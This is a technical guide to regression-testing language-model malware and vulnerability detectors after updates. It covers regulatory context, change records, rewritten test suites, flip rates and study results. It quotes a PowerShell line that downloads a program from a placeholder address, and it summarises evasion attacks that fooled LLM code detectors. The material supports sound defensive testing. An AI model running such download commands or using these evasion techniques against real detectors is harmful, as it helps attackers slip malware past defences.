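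The whole suite is quick enough to run after almost any change. At the speed Splunk reported, about 33 minutes for 1,000 scripts, a suite of 6,000 cases takes a little over three hours per model. People's time is harder to spare, especially for writing new variants and checking disputed labels, so the scale mainly limits how much of this work each change requires.

If several things change at once, the team should run the tests for the largest change. To find out which change caused a regression, it also has to test each change separately, for instance by running the old adapter with the new prompt.

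Small changes can also add up. If recall falls by half a percentage point in each of twelve monthly updates, each loss may look like normal variation, but recall ends the year six points lower. Comparing each candidate with a fixed older version, as well as with the current model, would expose the decline.

### Models that a supplier runs

A team that uses a supplier's online service usually can't store the weights, calculate their hash or restore an old version. It can record the model name and version it requested, any version label in the reply, the time, the prompt and settings it sent, and the answers it received. If the supplier offers a fixed version, the team should request it by its full name, because a general name may refer to whichever model is newest.

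ETSI recommends that developers help their customers evaluate model changes, for example through early access and versioned interfaces, but some suppliers document no fixed version. Even with a fixed version, the supplier may change the underlying hardware or software and will probably retire the version at some point. The record should include the retirement date so that the team can test the replacement while both versions are still available. After that date, the team can compare the replacement only with the old version's stored answers.

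A team that fine-tunes a model on the supplier's servers has the same problem. The team may never receive the adapter, and it loses the fine-tuned model when the supplier retires the base model. It then needs its own copy of the training data to train a replacement.

If a service has no fixed version, a test result describes it only at the time of the test. If repeated checks show an unexplained shift, the team should re-test as it would for a new base model, since it can't rule one out. The team also needs a fallback it controls, such as a small classifier or a set of detection rules. A contract can help by requiring advance notice of changes, including changes to compression and hidden instructions, and a period when both the old and new versions are available.

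### Official rules on recording and analysing changes

US federal agencies must apply controls from SP 800-53, a catalogue of security and privacy safeguards from the National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). Cloud suppliers that serve them must apply the same controls under FedRAMP, the government's authorisation programme. For other organisations, the catalogue is guidance unless a contract or another rule makes it binding.

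Control CM-3, which FedRAMP's *Configuration Management* reproduces, requires an organisation to decide which types of change need control, review each proposed change for its effects on security and privacy, approve or reject it, and document the decision. Control CM-4 requires an impact analysis before the change. NIST Mapper's *Impact Analyses (CM-4)*, a reference copy of the control, lists it for systems of low, moderate and high impact. A supplementary control, CM-4(2), adds a check after the change that the affected safeguards still produce the desired outcome.

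For a malware classifier, the desired outcome should include catching the attacks it caught before. But these controls apply to every kind of information system, and NIST specifies no test cases, comparison or pass mark for a model. The wording of CM-4 does not clearly prevent an agency from treating a higher score on held-out data as its entire impact analysis.

NIST is developing overlays that adapt the catalogue to AI. In a draft outline for fine-tuned models that predict or classify, NIST (2026) extends the baseline configuration, the approved description of a system, to machine-learning software, data pipelines and model settings. It warns that minor configuration changes could significantly alter a model's behaviour. It also proposes vulnerability scans after "significant AI model or pipeline changes", but does not define "significant". These scans look for software flaws and would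 not normally reveal that a classifier had begun to miss scripts. NIST also expects organisations to deploy only models that meet their quality metrics, which is closer to a re-test, but each organisation chooses the metrics.

The outline is not binding, and organisations may adopt NIST's suggestions in whole or in part. The outline's example uses are predicting equipment failures and screening job applicants. NIST planned to publish a fuller draft by the end of June 2026. In October it renamed the project after an executive order replaced "artificial intelligence" with "super intelligence" in government usage, and NIST's *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems* still offered the January outline for download, with no later draft.

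ETSI's standard is more specific about records. It is also voluntary, although national standards bodies had until 30 September 2026 to adopt it as a national standard. It requires organisations that follow it to have version control for their AI assets, and it requires operators to test a system before deploying it. It recommends that operators be able to restore a "known good state" and that developers log changes to prompts and other settings that affect how the system works.

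### When an update counts as a new system

ETSI recommends that developers treat a major update as a new version and repeat their security testing, but it doesn't define "major", so a team could class a monthly adapter update as minor and skip the tests. ETSI requires developers and operators to consider the security risks whenever they add or change a configuration option, but they could do this on paper without running any tests.

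The EU AI Act, which is binding law, attaches legal consequences to a "substantial modification" of a high-risk system. The European Commission's *Article 3* defines this as a change after release that the provider did not foresee or plan in its original assessment, and that either affects the system's compliance with the Act's high-risk requirements or alters the purpose for which the provider had it assessed. According to the Commission's *Recital 128*, a system modified this way counts as new and should undergo another conformity assessment, the procedure for demonstrating compliance.

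Most detectors of malicious scripts probably fall outside this rule. The Act's recitals do not count components intended solely for cybersecurity as safety components of critical infrastructure, and draft Commission guidelines repeat this exclusion, as McCann FitzGerald's *Critical Infrastructure Spotlight* explains. A tool that also evaluated employees' behaviour could still be high-risk under the Act's employment category. The duties for stand-alone high-risk systems will not apply until 2 December 2027, because an amendment that took effect in July 2026 postponed them, the National Law Review reports.

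For high-risk systems, the boundary remains uncertain. In *Evolving AI Systems under the AI Act*, Schnurr (2026) considers a hypothetical hiring tool. Its owner might retrain it on recent applications or lower the cut-off for the shortlist, or its supplier might replace the underlying model. Schnurr treats all three changes as open cases that depend partly on what the original assessment anticipated. The Commission's guidelines on the question were still in preparation in June 2026.

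Schnurr also cites EU product guidance that says a manufacturer need not repeat tests on aspects of a product that a modification doesn't affect. This makes sense for a machine with separate parts, but after fine-tuning, a team often can't know which behaviours are unaffected until it has tested them.

Companies that sell security software in the EU may have more reason to study the Cyber Resilience Act, which sets binding cybersecurity requirements for digital products and defines substantial modification in a similar way. Its main obligations apply from 11 December 2027. The European Commission announced non-binding advice on the term in July 2026, in *Commission publishes new guidance to support timely Cyber Resilience Act implementation*. Schnurr describes an earlier draft, in which the relevant factors included whether an update enables new attack scenarios or changes the likelihood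 of known risks. The law mainly concerns the security of the product itself, so it is unclear whether an update that makes a detector miss more malware would meet that test.

### Approving a range of updates in advance

Under the AI Act, a change can be a substantial modification only if it was unforeseen, so a provider can reduce uncertainty by planning its updates. The US Food and Drug Administration (FDA) has a developed scheme for planning updates to medical devices, called the predetermined change control plan. The manufacturer describes the changes it expects to make, how it will develop and test them, and their likely benefits and risks. The FDA reviews the plan with the device, and the manufacturer can then release updates that stay within the plan without applying again.

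A security team could approve its monthly fine-tuning rounds the same way. The plan might allow new adapters on the same base model if each one is trained on scripts from named sources and passes the same tests. A new base model or another scripting language would need separate approval. The team would still have to test every update, but it wouldn't have to debate each one.

A plan for one model may also leave out the systems that depend on it. In another of Schnurr's hypothetical cases, a hospital uses a model to score patients' risk before surgery, and a second system uses those scores to set its alarm thresholds. The model's supplier releases an improvement that its plan allows. The scores shift, and the alarms become less reliable although nobody has changed them. Similarly, if another tool ranks alerts by a script classifier's scores, the security team has to re-test that tool too when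 the classifier changes.

### A change record for a monthly fine-tuning round

The following record is for an imaginary team that updates its PowerShell classifier every month. The team has shortened the hashes for display.

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Record | PS-2026-12, opened 1 December 2026 |
| Reason for change | Two attacks missed in November; frequent false alarms on backup scripts |
| Current model | ps-11, in use since 9 November |
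| Candidate model | ps-12 |
| Base model | Foundation-Sec-8B-Instruct, local copy, hash 7c1e…; no change |
| Adapter | Rank 16, hash e40b…; training started from the base model, not from ps-11 |
| Training data | Snapshot of 30 November: 24,000 earlier scripts and 1,400 new ones |
| Sources of new scripts | 1,090 from a commercial feed, half of them malicious; 310 analyst corrections, comprising 290 false alarms and 20 missed attacks |
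| Overlap check | 14 scripts also in the suite or held-out set; team removed them before training |
| Training settings | Settings file 8, random seed 31 |
| Prompt | Version 5, without retrieved examples; no change |
| Threshold | 0.60, provisional |
| Decoding | Temperature 0; scripts over 8,000 tokens go to an analyst |
| Inference software | Server version 4.2 since 20 November, previously 4.1; 16-bit weights, separate adapter |
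| Regression suite | Version 14: 4,000 malicious and 2,000 benign cases |
| Past results for ps-11 | 5 November, server version 4.1: 3,884 attacks caught, 58 false alarms; answers and scores for each case in results file 11 |
| Required re-test | Whole suite on both models, held-out set, prompt-injection tests, threshold check, 200 new variants |
| Version to restore if needed | ps-11 with prompt 5, threshold 0.60 and server version 4.2; trial restoration on 1 December |
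| Candidate results and decision | Blank until testing ends |

The server changed after the team last tested ps-11, so the old results are not a fair baseline for ps-12. The team has to test both models on version 4.2, or it won't be able to separate the effects of the new software from those of training.

The analysts' corrections are also lopsided because analysts mostly review alerts. Of the 310 corrections, 290 label a script benign and only 20 label one malicious. Across all the new data, 835 scripts are benign and 565 are malicious. The round may well reduce false alarms on backup scripts, but it could also make the model more likely to miss attacks that resemble them. The team should therefore base some of its 200 new variants on malicious scripts that copy or compress files as a backup script does.

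## Building a regression suite from transformed inputs

A regression suite tests the model against disguises the team has chosen, rather than whichever ones happen to be in a held-out set. The team selects seed inputs, rewrites them, checks that each variant still does what its seed did, and labels the cases. It then groups them by seed and threat family and freezes the result as a numbered version. Checking behaviour needs the most care, because a variant that no longer works as an attack makes the test wrong.

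### Choosing seeds

A threat family is a group of attacks that share a method. Fetterman sorted PowerShell scripts into seven families by the suspicious command they contained. Of the 293 pairs in the main collection, 146 involved DownloadFile, which saves a file from the web, and only 7 involved -EncodedCommand, which runs a command stored as encoded text. A random sample from it would include very few encoded commands. The team can set a minimum for each family, such as 30 seeds, and look for more scripts for any family below it.

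Thirty seeds are much less useful if they are copies of one another, and attackers reuse scripts constantly. In *Syntax- and Compilation-Preserving Evasion of LLM Vulnerability Detectors*, Sun, Oprea and Wong (2026) pooled vulnerable functions from three public collections. To remove duplicates, they stripped comments, collapsed runs of spaces and compared hashes of the remaining text. This catches copies that differ only in comments or spacing. For malicious scripts, the team should also replace web addresses and variable names with placeholders before hashing, since the same script often circulates with a new address.

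Fetterman's rule of using only seeds that the model already classified correctly works for a single experiment, but a regression suite has to last through many updates. The team should also keep the seeds that the current model misses and record each miss. If an updated model detects one of these seeds and a later model misses it again, that is a security regression, which the team would not see if it had discarded the seed.

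### Choosing rewrites and generating variants

The team should begin with rewrites that attackers are known to use. MITRE ATT&CK's *Obfuscated Files or Information* (2023), part of a public catalogue of attack techniques, describes splitting text into pieces, mixing upper and lower case, hiding text in environment variables, and encoding commands in Base64. Among the groups it lists, FIN7 has used split text and environment variables, and APT32 and MuddyWater have used a public tool that automatically disguises PowerShell.

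Any regression suite for scripts should include Base64 encoding, which appears repeatedly in the catalogue. It should also include simple rewrites, because Foundation-Sec caught the Base64 variants but missed scripts that used a short command name.

To generate variants for the three tiers, from direct replacements to changes of letter case, Fetterman's pipeline applies each rewrite only to scripts where it makes sense. A rewrite that hides Invoke-WebRequest, for instance, goes only to seeds that contain that command. This published pair comes from the first tier, with the web address replaced here by a placeholder:

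| Version | Script |
|---|---|
| Seed | `Invoke-WebRequest -Uri ADDRESS -OutFile c:\temp\sendme.exe` |
| Variant | `iwr -Uri ADDRESS -OutFile c:\temp\sendme.exe` |

Both lines download a program and save it under a different name. Microsoft lists the short name for every platform, so the two lines do the same thing.

Because only one thing differs between seed and variant, the team knows which change caused a miss. Real attackers combine several disguises, so the suite should also include some variants with more than one. *Characterizing Robustness in Semantic Code Clone Detection* (2026) tested combinations drawn from a set of 51 rewrites on models that judge whether two pieces of code do the same job. One model, CodeBERT, lost 46.77 points of F1 on one dataset, or 49.18 points when pairs that the rewrites had left unchanged were excluded. A team should remove unchanged variants from its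 own suite because they add easy passes. The study also found that models with similar scores on the original code could differ widely on the rewritten code.

Some rewrites apply to very few inputs. In *Semantic-Preserving Transformations as Mutation Operators*, Hort, Vidziunas and Moonen (2025) tried 16 rewrites on 2,732 C and C++ functions. Four rewrites worked on every function, and some worked on only three. The team should count the finished cases for each combination of family and rewrite, because passing "all loop rewrites" means little if there were only three cases.

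### Checking that the behaviour is the same

A rewrite that breaks a malicious script produces an invalid variant, which can mislead the team in two ways. If the candidate model labels the broken script benign, the suite records a missed attack even though the script is harmless. The team may then reject a good model or train it to flag broken scripts. If the candidate labels the broken script malicious, the team counts this as evidence that the model can detect disguised attacks, even though no attacker could use that disguise.

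Published code transformations need checking before reuse. Hort and colleagues found 94 transformations in 28 publications, all described as preserving what the code does. They took 39 from four publications that shared their software, ran them on a collection of C and C++ functions, and read up to 20 results for each. They found that 23 changed the meaning of at least one function, and kept the other 16.

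These failures had ordinary causes. One rewrite moved the definition of a counter inside a loop, although a later loop still needed it. A renaming tool didn't account for functions that contained assembly code, which gives instructions directly to the processor. Other rewrites were written for whole files, but the collection held single functions. A team therefore has to test each rewrite on its own inputs. The result doesn't mean that most published rewrites are wrong, since some of these tools may have worked properly on the data they were designed for.

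The 16 remaining rewrites may contain errors too, as Hort and colleagues acknowledge. A rewrite that makes no mistakes in 20 outputs could still break up to about 14% of inputs, at 95% confidence. To rule out a failure rate above 1%, a team would have to check about 300 outputs and find no errors. Most teams can't do that by hand for every rewrite, so they also need automatic checks.

Fetterman's pipeline first parses each variant, which means checking that it follows the grammar of the language. It uses PowerShell's own parser where the required version is available and a general parsing tool called Tree-sitter elsewhere. It then tests invariants, properties that must be the same in seed and variant:

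- the set of web addresses
- the names of programs and file paths
- the decoded content of any encoded command
- the arguments of the rewritten command, such as what it requests or which program it starts

The pair above passes because the address, the file path and both arguments are identical. To cover a new family, a team would write a filter for seeds, a list of allowed rewrites, any PowerShell version requirements, and invariants. For scripts that create scheduled tasks, the invariants might be the program the task runs, the program's arguments and the task's timing.

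The version requirement matters even for aliases. In Windows PowerShell 5.1, "curl" is an alias for Invoke-WebRequest, but Microsoft notes that it hides a separate curl program that takes different parameters. Microsoft's documentation for newer versions lists only "iwr" as an alias. The same replacement can therefore be valid on one machine but break the script or change what it does on another.

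These checks examine a script's text without running it, so they miss some errors. For example, if a rewrite moved a download after the command that opens the downloaded file, the script would still parse and keep every address, path and argument intact, but the attack would fail.

For compiled languages, compiling is a stricter check than parsing. Sun and colleagues renamed variables in vulnerable functions and found that about 98% of the renamed functions had no new syntax errors. In a separate set of 1,434 functions that compiled before renaming, 1,303 (90.9%) still compiled afterward. The other 131 failed because the new names clashed with names in standard files that the researchers had added to make the functions compile. Sun and colleagues counted these failures as unsuccessful attacks, which avoids exaggerating the danger. In a regression suite, the same rule would count broken cases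 as passes, so the team should remove them.

The strongest practical check is to run the seed and the variant in an isolated environment and compare what they do. The 2025 study *Leveraging LLM to Strengthen ML-Based Cross-Site Scripting Detection* did this for scripts that attackers plant in web pages. It had a language model disguise the scripts, then compared the alerts and other actions that each version triggered. Many, but not all, of the disguised scripts still worked as before. Language models can produce more varied disguises than fixed rules can, and their output needs this check most.

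If the attacker's server is offline when the team runs the scripts, the seed and the variant may both stop at the first download, so their identical behaviour is only weak evidence that they are equivalent. The team can set up a substitute server that supplies a harmless file, so that both scripts run to the end. It can limit this work to a sample of variants from each rewrite and every variant that the candidate misses.

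### Source code and phishing messages

For a detector of vulnerable code, a good seed is a vulnerable function together with its patched version. Transformations might include renaming variables, turning one kind of loop into another, or adding code that never runs. Renaming variables is the most common, used in 25 of the 28 publications that Hort and colleagues reviewed.

A rewrite must preserve the flaw, but it can remove it by accident. The 94 published rewrites include adding checks on a function's inputs and switching to larger number types. Either might be harmless when the task is to identify a program's author, but a new input check could repair a missing one, and a larger number type could prevent an overflow. If the team has an input that triggers the flaw, it can run that input on the vulnerable function, the patched function and all their variants. Only the vulnerable function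 and its variants should fail. Many public collections contain isolated functions that can't run by themselves, so the team may have to build this part of the suite from its own software.

No parser or compiler can check whether a rewritten phishing message is still phishing. The team could group seeds by pretext, such as a fake invoice or a password reset, and rewrite them by paraphrasing, translating, changing the layout or replacing letters with lookalikes. The invariants would be the impersonated organisation, the requested action and the link's destination. A paraphrase that drops the false claim about the sender may turn a phishing message into an ordinary request, so two people should read each variant without seeing its intended label, and the team should drop any variant they disagree on.

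### Labels and benign counterparts

Each variant takes its seed's label, so a mislabelled seed with seven variants adds eight wrong cases to the suite. An expert should confirm every seed's label before the team generates variants from it. Public collections of vulnerable code contain many doubtful labels, so this check may rule out many candidate seeds from those sources.

The team also needs rewritten benign inputs, so that a model can't pass by flagging anything unusual. Many harmless scripts look unusual because administrators use short command names to save typing and software companies compress or encode their scripts. The best benign case is a harmless script from the same family as the malicious one, rewritten the same way. If the model flags both an attack and a routine download that use iwr, it may have learned to treat the short name itself as evidence of an attack.

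Sun and colleagues tested five of their six models on 500 safe functions. GPT-5-mini, the model that best resisted their attacks, flagged 272 of them (54.4%), and the specialised detector CodeAstra flagged 350 (70%). After the researchers applied their rewrites, every safe function that a model had labelled correctly kept its label. They had designed the rewrites to push models towards the answer "benign", so this result doesn't show how often ordinary disguises cause false alarms.

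A weak detector's individual misses also carry little information. The two models that Hort and colleagues tested were only 62% to 65% accurate on the original functions, and they changed their answer on 49% of rewritten functions, about equally often in each direction. When the researchers labeled each function by a vote over the predictions for its rewritten copies, accuracy fell to between 48% and 51%, roughly the same as guessing. If a model behaves like this, the team should improve it before building a detailed suite around it.

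A miss can also come from the scoring software instead of the model's judgement. *Robustness of LLM-Generated SystemVerilog Assertions to Semantics-Preserving RTL Transformations* (2026), which studied models that write formal checks for chip designs, inspected 30 answers that had gone from right to wrong after the input was rewritten. Twenty-eight contained real errors, and the other two had only broken the required answer format. Similarly, a detector that replies "this script is malicious" when the software expects "malicious" could be wrongly scored as a miss.

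### Scoring by seed

Variants of one seed are not independent. *Fool Me If You Can*, a 2026 study that tested models that compare compiled programs, used 9,565 variants made from 620 seeds, or about 15 each. If a model fails on one seed because of some peculiarity, it may fail on all 15 variants, and counting each variant separately would turn one problem into 15 findings.

Some seeds also accept many more rewrites than others, which distorts an average. Suppose a small suite has four malicious seeds:

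| Seed | Variants | Caught |
|---|---|---|
| A | 40 | 40 |
| B | 2 | 1 |
| C | 2 | 1 |
| D | 2 | 1 |

The model catches 43 of the 46 variants, or 93%. To score by seed, the team calculates the share of variants caught for each seed and then averages those shares. The result is (100% + 50% + 50% + 50%) / 4, or 62.5%, and seed A no longer dominates it. The team should also calculate this score for each threat family, since the overall score can hide a sharp drop in one of them.

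Uncertainty estimates need the same grouping. The SystemVerilog study resampled whole pairs of original and rewritten designs, not the separate behaviours within them. A security team that resampled individual variants would underestimate the uncertainty in its results.

### Complete Resistance

An attacker who can try several disguises needs only one to work. In the example, the model catches every variant of seed A only, so an attacker who could try every disguise would succeed with three of the four seeds. Sun and colleagues measure this worst case with Complete Resistance (CR):

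CR = detected threats that the model still catches after every rewrite / all threats detected in their original form

Their test set held 5,000 vulnerable C and C++ functions. They made five variants of each function a model had detected, by renaming a variable or by placing text in a comment, an unused macro, a disabled block or a branch that never runs. An automatic search chose the inserted text to mislead a model. In one test, the search used a different model from the one under attack, and in the other it used the target itself. The counts below follow from the published rates, and the last column covers the 500 safe functions:

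| Model | Detected, of 5,000 | CR, text tuned on another model | CR, text tuned on this model | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 1,552 | 5 (0.32%) | 2 (0.13%) | 17% |
| CodeAstra | 3,454 | about 173 (5.00%) | 4 (0.12%) | 70% |
| StarCoder2 15B | 4,952 | 608 (12.28%) | 476 (9.61%) | not listed |
| Qwen2.5-Coder 32B | 1,121 | 7 (0.62%) | not measured | 11% |
| GPT-4o | 2,300 | 299 (13.00%) | not measured | 36% |
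| GPT-5-mini | 3,681 | 2,060 (55.96%) | not measured | 54% |

The average over variants can hide a large difference in CR. With text tuned on another model, StarCoder2 and GPT-5-mini both still caught about 81% of variants on average, so a team that looked only at the average would rate them as equally robust. But StarCoder2's failures came almost entirely from the unused macro, which made it miss 87% of functions, and its CR was 12%. GPT-5-mini's failures were spread more evenly and often fell on the same functions, so its CR was 56%.

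The average and the breakdown by rewrite are still useful because CR alone wouldn't show that StarCoder2 has one severe weakness, which might be easier to repair than moderate weaknesses against every rewrite. CR also assumes an attacker who can keep trying until something works. That is realistic if the attacker has a copy of the model or sees its verdicts, but pessimistic if the attacker gets only one attempt.

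CR can mislead a team comparing versions in two ways. First, adding a rewrite to the suite can only lower CR or leave it unchanged, so the team can compare CR only between models tested on the same rewrites. Second, the denominator is the number of seeds the model detects before rewriting, which varies by model. Suppose the current model detects 900 of 1,000 malicious seeds and still detects 600 of them under every rewrite, for a CR of 67%. The candidate detects 750 and still detects 560 under every rewrite, for a CR of 75%. The candidate looks more robust, although it catches fewer attacks both before and after rewriting. Dividing by all 1,000 seeds instead avoids this problem, giving 60% for the current model and 56% for the candidate.

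Sun and colleagues measured the models' resistance to carefully tuned text, much of which looks unnatural and might alert a human reviewer. Random renaming fooled the models on only 7% to 30% of detected functions. All six models date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may do better. The researchers checked the functions' grammar and whether some of them compiled, but could not run them to confirm identical behaviour.

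### Fixed suites and attacks fitted to the candidate

A regression suite stays the same when the model changes, but a determined attacker studies the new model and looks for ways to defeat it. The team can imitate this by searching each candidate model afresh for weaknesses, often as part of red-teaming, in which people or programs deliberately attack a system to test it.

| | Fixed suite | Attacks fitted to each candidate |
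|---|---|---|
| Finds | Lost detections among known threats and rewrites | New weaknesses, including any that the update created |
| Costs | Much work to build, then a few hours of computing per model | A new search each time, with specialist staff and often many hours of computing |
| Misses | Weaknesses outside the suite | Weaknesses that the search happens not to reach |

A fixed suite can badly underestimate how often a new search would fool the model. Sun and colleagues renamed variables with text tuned on a smaller model and fooled Qwen2.5-Coder 32B on 302 of the 1,121 functions it had detected, or 27%. When they tuned the text on the 32B model itself, they fooled it on 1,038, or 93%. The search for this one type of rewrite took about 20 hours on one high-end graphics processor.

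Yet a new search doesn't always find more. Tuning the attacks on CodeAstra itself raised the success rate of renaming from 5% to 85% but lowered that of text in disabled blocks from 43% to 17%. The researchers suspect that the search got stuck. A team that ran only the new search would have underestimated the second weakness, which the older, fixed attack had already exposed.

Attackers may not need the model's weights for such a search. In *Shield broken*, Jiang, Huang, Treude and colleagues (2026) evaded the vulnerability detector LineVul in 49% of attempts using only the labels it returned. Fitted attacks are therefore a greater concern when outsiders can see a detector's verdicts.

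Fitted attacks are poorly suited to comparing two versions, because the test changes along with the model. Their results also vary by chance. Sun and colleagues repeated the renaming search against Llama 3.1 8B with three different sets of training examples, and its average success was 31%, with a standard deviation of 11 points. A candidate that seems ten points more robust than the current model may only have faced a less successful search. The fixed suite is better for deciding whether an update made something worse, while fitted attacks are more useful for finding out how badly a version could fail. When a fitted attack succeeds, the team can save the result as a fixed case and run it on both versions.

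### Freezing a version and adding new cases

Once the cases have passed their checks, the team stores them with a version number and a hash. The imaginary PowerShell team's version 14 has 500 malicious seeds with an average of seven variants each, which makes 4,000 malicious cases, and 250 benign seeds with the same average, which makes 2,000. Each case has an entry like this one:

| Field | Entry |
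|---|---|
| Case | 0217-03 |
| Seed and family | 0217, web download |
| Label | Malicious; two analysts confirmed the seed |
| Rewrite | Short command name |
| Checks | PowerShell 7 parser; same address, path and arguments; matching test runs |
| Source | Incident in August 2026 |
| Part | Open |

If someone finds an invalid case, the team removes it in the next version and records the reason. The team never edits a frozen version, since old results would then refer to cases that no longer exist. After any change to the suite, it also runs the current model on the new version so that it can compare both models on the same cases.

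Incidents are the best source of new seeds because they show what real attackers did. After the model misses an attack, an analyst confirms the label and removes passwords and personal data. The team then generates variants, since the attacker may return with a slightly different script. The team adds red-team findings the same way, after the same validity checks.

People who write detection rules routinely keep old attacks for testing. Splunk, for example, tests its rules on *Obfuscated Powershell*, a set of logs from disguised PowerShell commands that it recorded in January 2021. These logs can still show whether a detector can no longer detect attacks it used to catch, but they contain no disguises invented since then.

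### Keeping part of the suite secret

If engineers can see every test case, they may keep adjusting the prompt, the threshold and the training data until the candidate passes, without making it better at catching other disguised scripts. NIST makes the same distinction between a model's accuracy on one fixed set of questions and its accuracy on all similar questions.

The team can guard against this by keeping some seeds and their variants secret from the people who train the model. The imaginary team might reserve 100 of its 500 malicious seeds and 50 of its 250 benign ones. Someone outside the training group runs them and reports only the totals for each family. Where possible, the secret set should include a few rewrites that don't appear in the open set. If the candidate does well on the open cases and badly on the secret ones, it has probably adapted to the suite.

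NIST uses the same idea in a testing programme it announced in July 2026. PYMNTS's *NIST Launches AI Model Evaluation Program to Benchmark Performance* reports that developers can't see the test data, which reduces the risk that it ends up in their training sets. The programme starts with models that interpret images and text in genomics, quantum science and public safety, so security teams can use it as a precedent but not as a ready-made test.

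The secret seeds gradually become known, because each report reveals a little about them and engineers eventually need to see the failures to fix them. Once engineers have seen a case, the team should move it to the open part and replace it with a new one. Replacing a quarter of the secret seeds every three months would renew the whole set within a year. Someone other than the author should check the new cases, because nobody else will be able to notice mistakes in them.

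The team must also keep the whole suite out of the training data. The safest method is to assign each seed to training or testing before generating variants, and keep all its variants in the same set. If the team split the variants at random, the model could train on one version of a script and be tested on another. It would then look robust because it recognised the unchanged parts of the script.

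Before each fine-tuning round, the team checks the new training data for overlap with the suite. Comparing hashes finds exact copies. Replacing addresses and variable names with placeholders, as the team did to remove duplicate seeds, finds copies in which only those details changed. Expanding short command names and decoding encoded text before comparing will reveal more copies. Searching for long stretches of shared text can find scripts that have only a section in common.

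To help detect accidental leaks, the team can place a canary, which is a unique random string, in the suite's files but outside the scripts. If a language model assigns the canary a much higher probability than other random strings of the same length, it was probably trained on those files (tianpan.co, 2026). This check can miss a leak if someone deletes the canary to hide the leak, or if an automatic process extracts only the scripts.

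Some failed cases will be useful as training examples when the team repairs a regression. Once a seed or any of its variants has been used in training, a pass on that seed no longer shows that the model can handle unfamiliar scripts. The team should mark the seed and all its variants as used, keep them only to check that the repair lasts, and write new cases from other seeds in the same family.

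## Comparing the current and candidate models case by case

After freezing the test suite, the team runs the current and candidate models on the same cases and compares their answers one by one to see which attacks the candidate no longer catches and whether those attacks have something in common. It must then work out how many of the differences would have appeared without an update, and whether a loss on a few cases is likely to extend to similar attacks outside the suite.

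### Negative and positive flips

A negative flip is a case that the current model gets right and the candidate gets wrong, and a positive flip is the reverse. The negative flip rate (NFR) is the number of negative flips divided by the number of cases tested. The positive flip rate (PFR) is the same calculation for positive flips.

Suppose a team tests both models on 2,000 variants of malicious scripts:

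| | Candidate catches | Candidate misses | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Current model catches | 1,710 | 90 | 1,800 |
| Current model misses | 120 | 80 | 200 |
| Total | 1,830 | 170 | 2,000 |

The current model's accuracy is the share of cases that both models get right plus the NFR. The candidate's accuracy is that same share plus the PFR. Subtracting the candidate's accuracy from the current model's leaves

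loss in accuracy = NFR − PFR

Here the NFR is 4.5% and the PFR is 6.0%, so accuracy rises by 1.5 points, from 90% to 91.5%. Every variant is malicious, so all 90 negative flips are security regressions. Their number can't be worked out from the totals alone, because a rise from 1,800 to 1,830 correct results could include anywhere from 0 to 170 negative flips.

Suppose that 60 of the 90 cases that got worse belong to one threat family with 80 variants. The NFR in that family is 75%, so if the current model caught all 80 variants, the candidate catches only 20. In the rest of the suite, 30 of 1,920 cases get worse, or 1.6%. The overall NFR is still 4.5% and accuracy still rises by 1.5 points, but an attacker who uses that family would usually get past the candidate. The team therefore needs the NFR for each family and a list of the cases that got worse.

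The comparison also needs separate negative flip rates for malicious and benign cases. A candidate that labels every script malicious has no negative flips on malicious scripts, but has one on every benign script that the current model labelled correctly.

Published rates do not all use the same denominator. *No Universal Signal Predicts Sample-Level LLM Regression under Version Updates* (Sheng and Lu, 2026) divides by only the cases that the old model got right. In the example, that gives 90 out of 1,800, or 5.0%. The two rates differ more when the current model is weak. If it catches 200 of 2,000 attacks and the candidate misses 100 of those 200, the NFR is 5% of all cases but 50% of the attacks the current model caught.

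### New errors and the size of the gain

Security companies were counting such errors before researchers working on image classifiers introduced the term "negative flip" in 2021. Krisiloff called them "bad churn" in 2019. FireEye corrected some of its models' mistakes with lists of approved and blocked items, so a new mistake could require a new entry. Krisiloff recommended testing each update on a large collection of files to find new mistakes.

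In Krisiloff's retraining experiment with Windows program files, the retrained detector made 246 new errors, or 0.12% of the files tested. Accuracy rose by 0.23 points, so the PFR must have been about 0.35%. The detector corrected roughly three old errors for each new one.

Krisiloff expected larger gains in accuracy to bring more new errors, since a bigger improvement usually requires a bigger change in the model's boundary between malicious and benign. *MUSCLE* (2024), which studied language-model tasks after a change of base model, found more negative flips where the gain was smaller. The models and tasks were very different, so both patterns may be real. Neither lets a team estimate the number of negative flips from the size of the gain.

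Running the whole test suite takes longer than re-testing only the cases where the current model was unsure, but it is safer. Sheng and Lu examined whether low confidence predicts which answers will flip, using five updates of open models with seven to nine billion parameters. They paired questions that flipped with questions that stayed right, and checked how often the old model had been less confident about the one that flipped. On a multiple-choice benchmark this happened 74% to 84% of the time, compared with 50% by chance. On a set of programming tasks it happened only 44% to 64% of the time. A detector that outputs one label is closer to the multiple-choice case, but even there many flips occur on answers the old model had seemed confident about.

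### Security regressions in Android malware detectors

In *Regression-aware Continual Learning for Android Malware Detection*, Ghiani, Angioni and colleagues measured security regressions over a long series of updates. They used two collections of apps, which they labelled using antivirus scanners' verdicts. ELSA has 75,000 apps from 2017 to 2019, a tenth of them malicious, and TESSERACT has more than 230,000 from 2014 to 2018. They divided each collection into three-month windows and updated the detector once per window. After each update, they compared the new version with the previous one on test apps from every window so far.

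Most of the experiments used a small neural network that works from a checklist of each app's characteristics. The researchers also tried a simpler linear model and a larger network that reads the app's instructions, but none of the three was a language model.

| Collection and detector | Training data for each update | NFR on malware | NFR on benign apps |
|---|---|---|---|
| ELSA, small network | New window only | 3.17% | 0.48% |
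| ELSA, small network | All windows so far | 1.16% | 0.23% |
| TESSERACT, small network | New window only | 2.92% | 0.27% |
| TESSERACT, small network | All windows so far | 0.54% | 0.07% |
| ELSA, linear model | New window only | 6.13% | Not reported |
| ELSA, larger network | New window only | 7.08% | 1.84% |
| ELSA, larger network | All windows so far | 2.91% | 1.05% |

Ghiani and colleagues summarise their results as regressions in "up to 3-6%" of malware. This range describes the less favourable combinations of detector and training method, and the larger network exceeded it. Retraining on all the old data reduced regressions considerably but did not eliminate them. In their introduction, they describe the figures as shares of previously detected malware, but their formula divides by all malware tested. The small network detected about 84% of ELSA's malware, so a regression rate of 3.17%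 of all malware is about 3.8% of the malware it had previously detected.

The rates are also averages over small groups. Each ELSA window had about 125 malicious test apps, so an NFR of 3.17% is about four apps per window after each update. Nine-tenths of the ELSA apps were benign, and pooling the two classes would have given an NFR of about 0.75%, making the problem hard to see.

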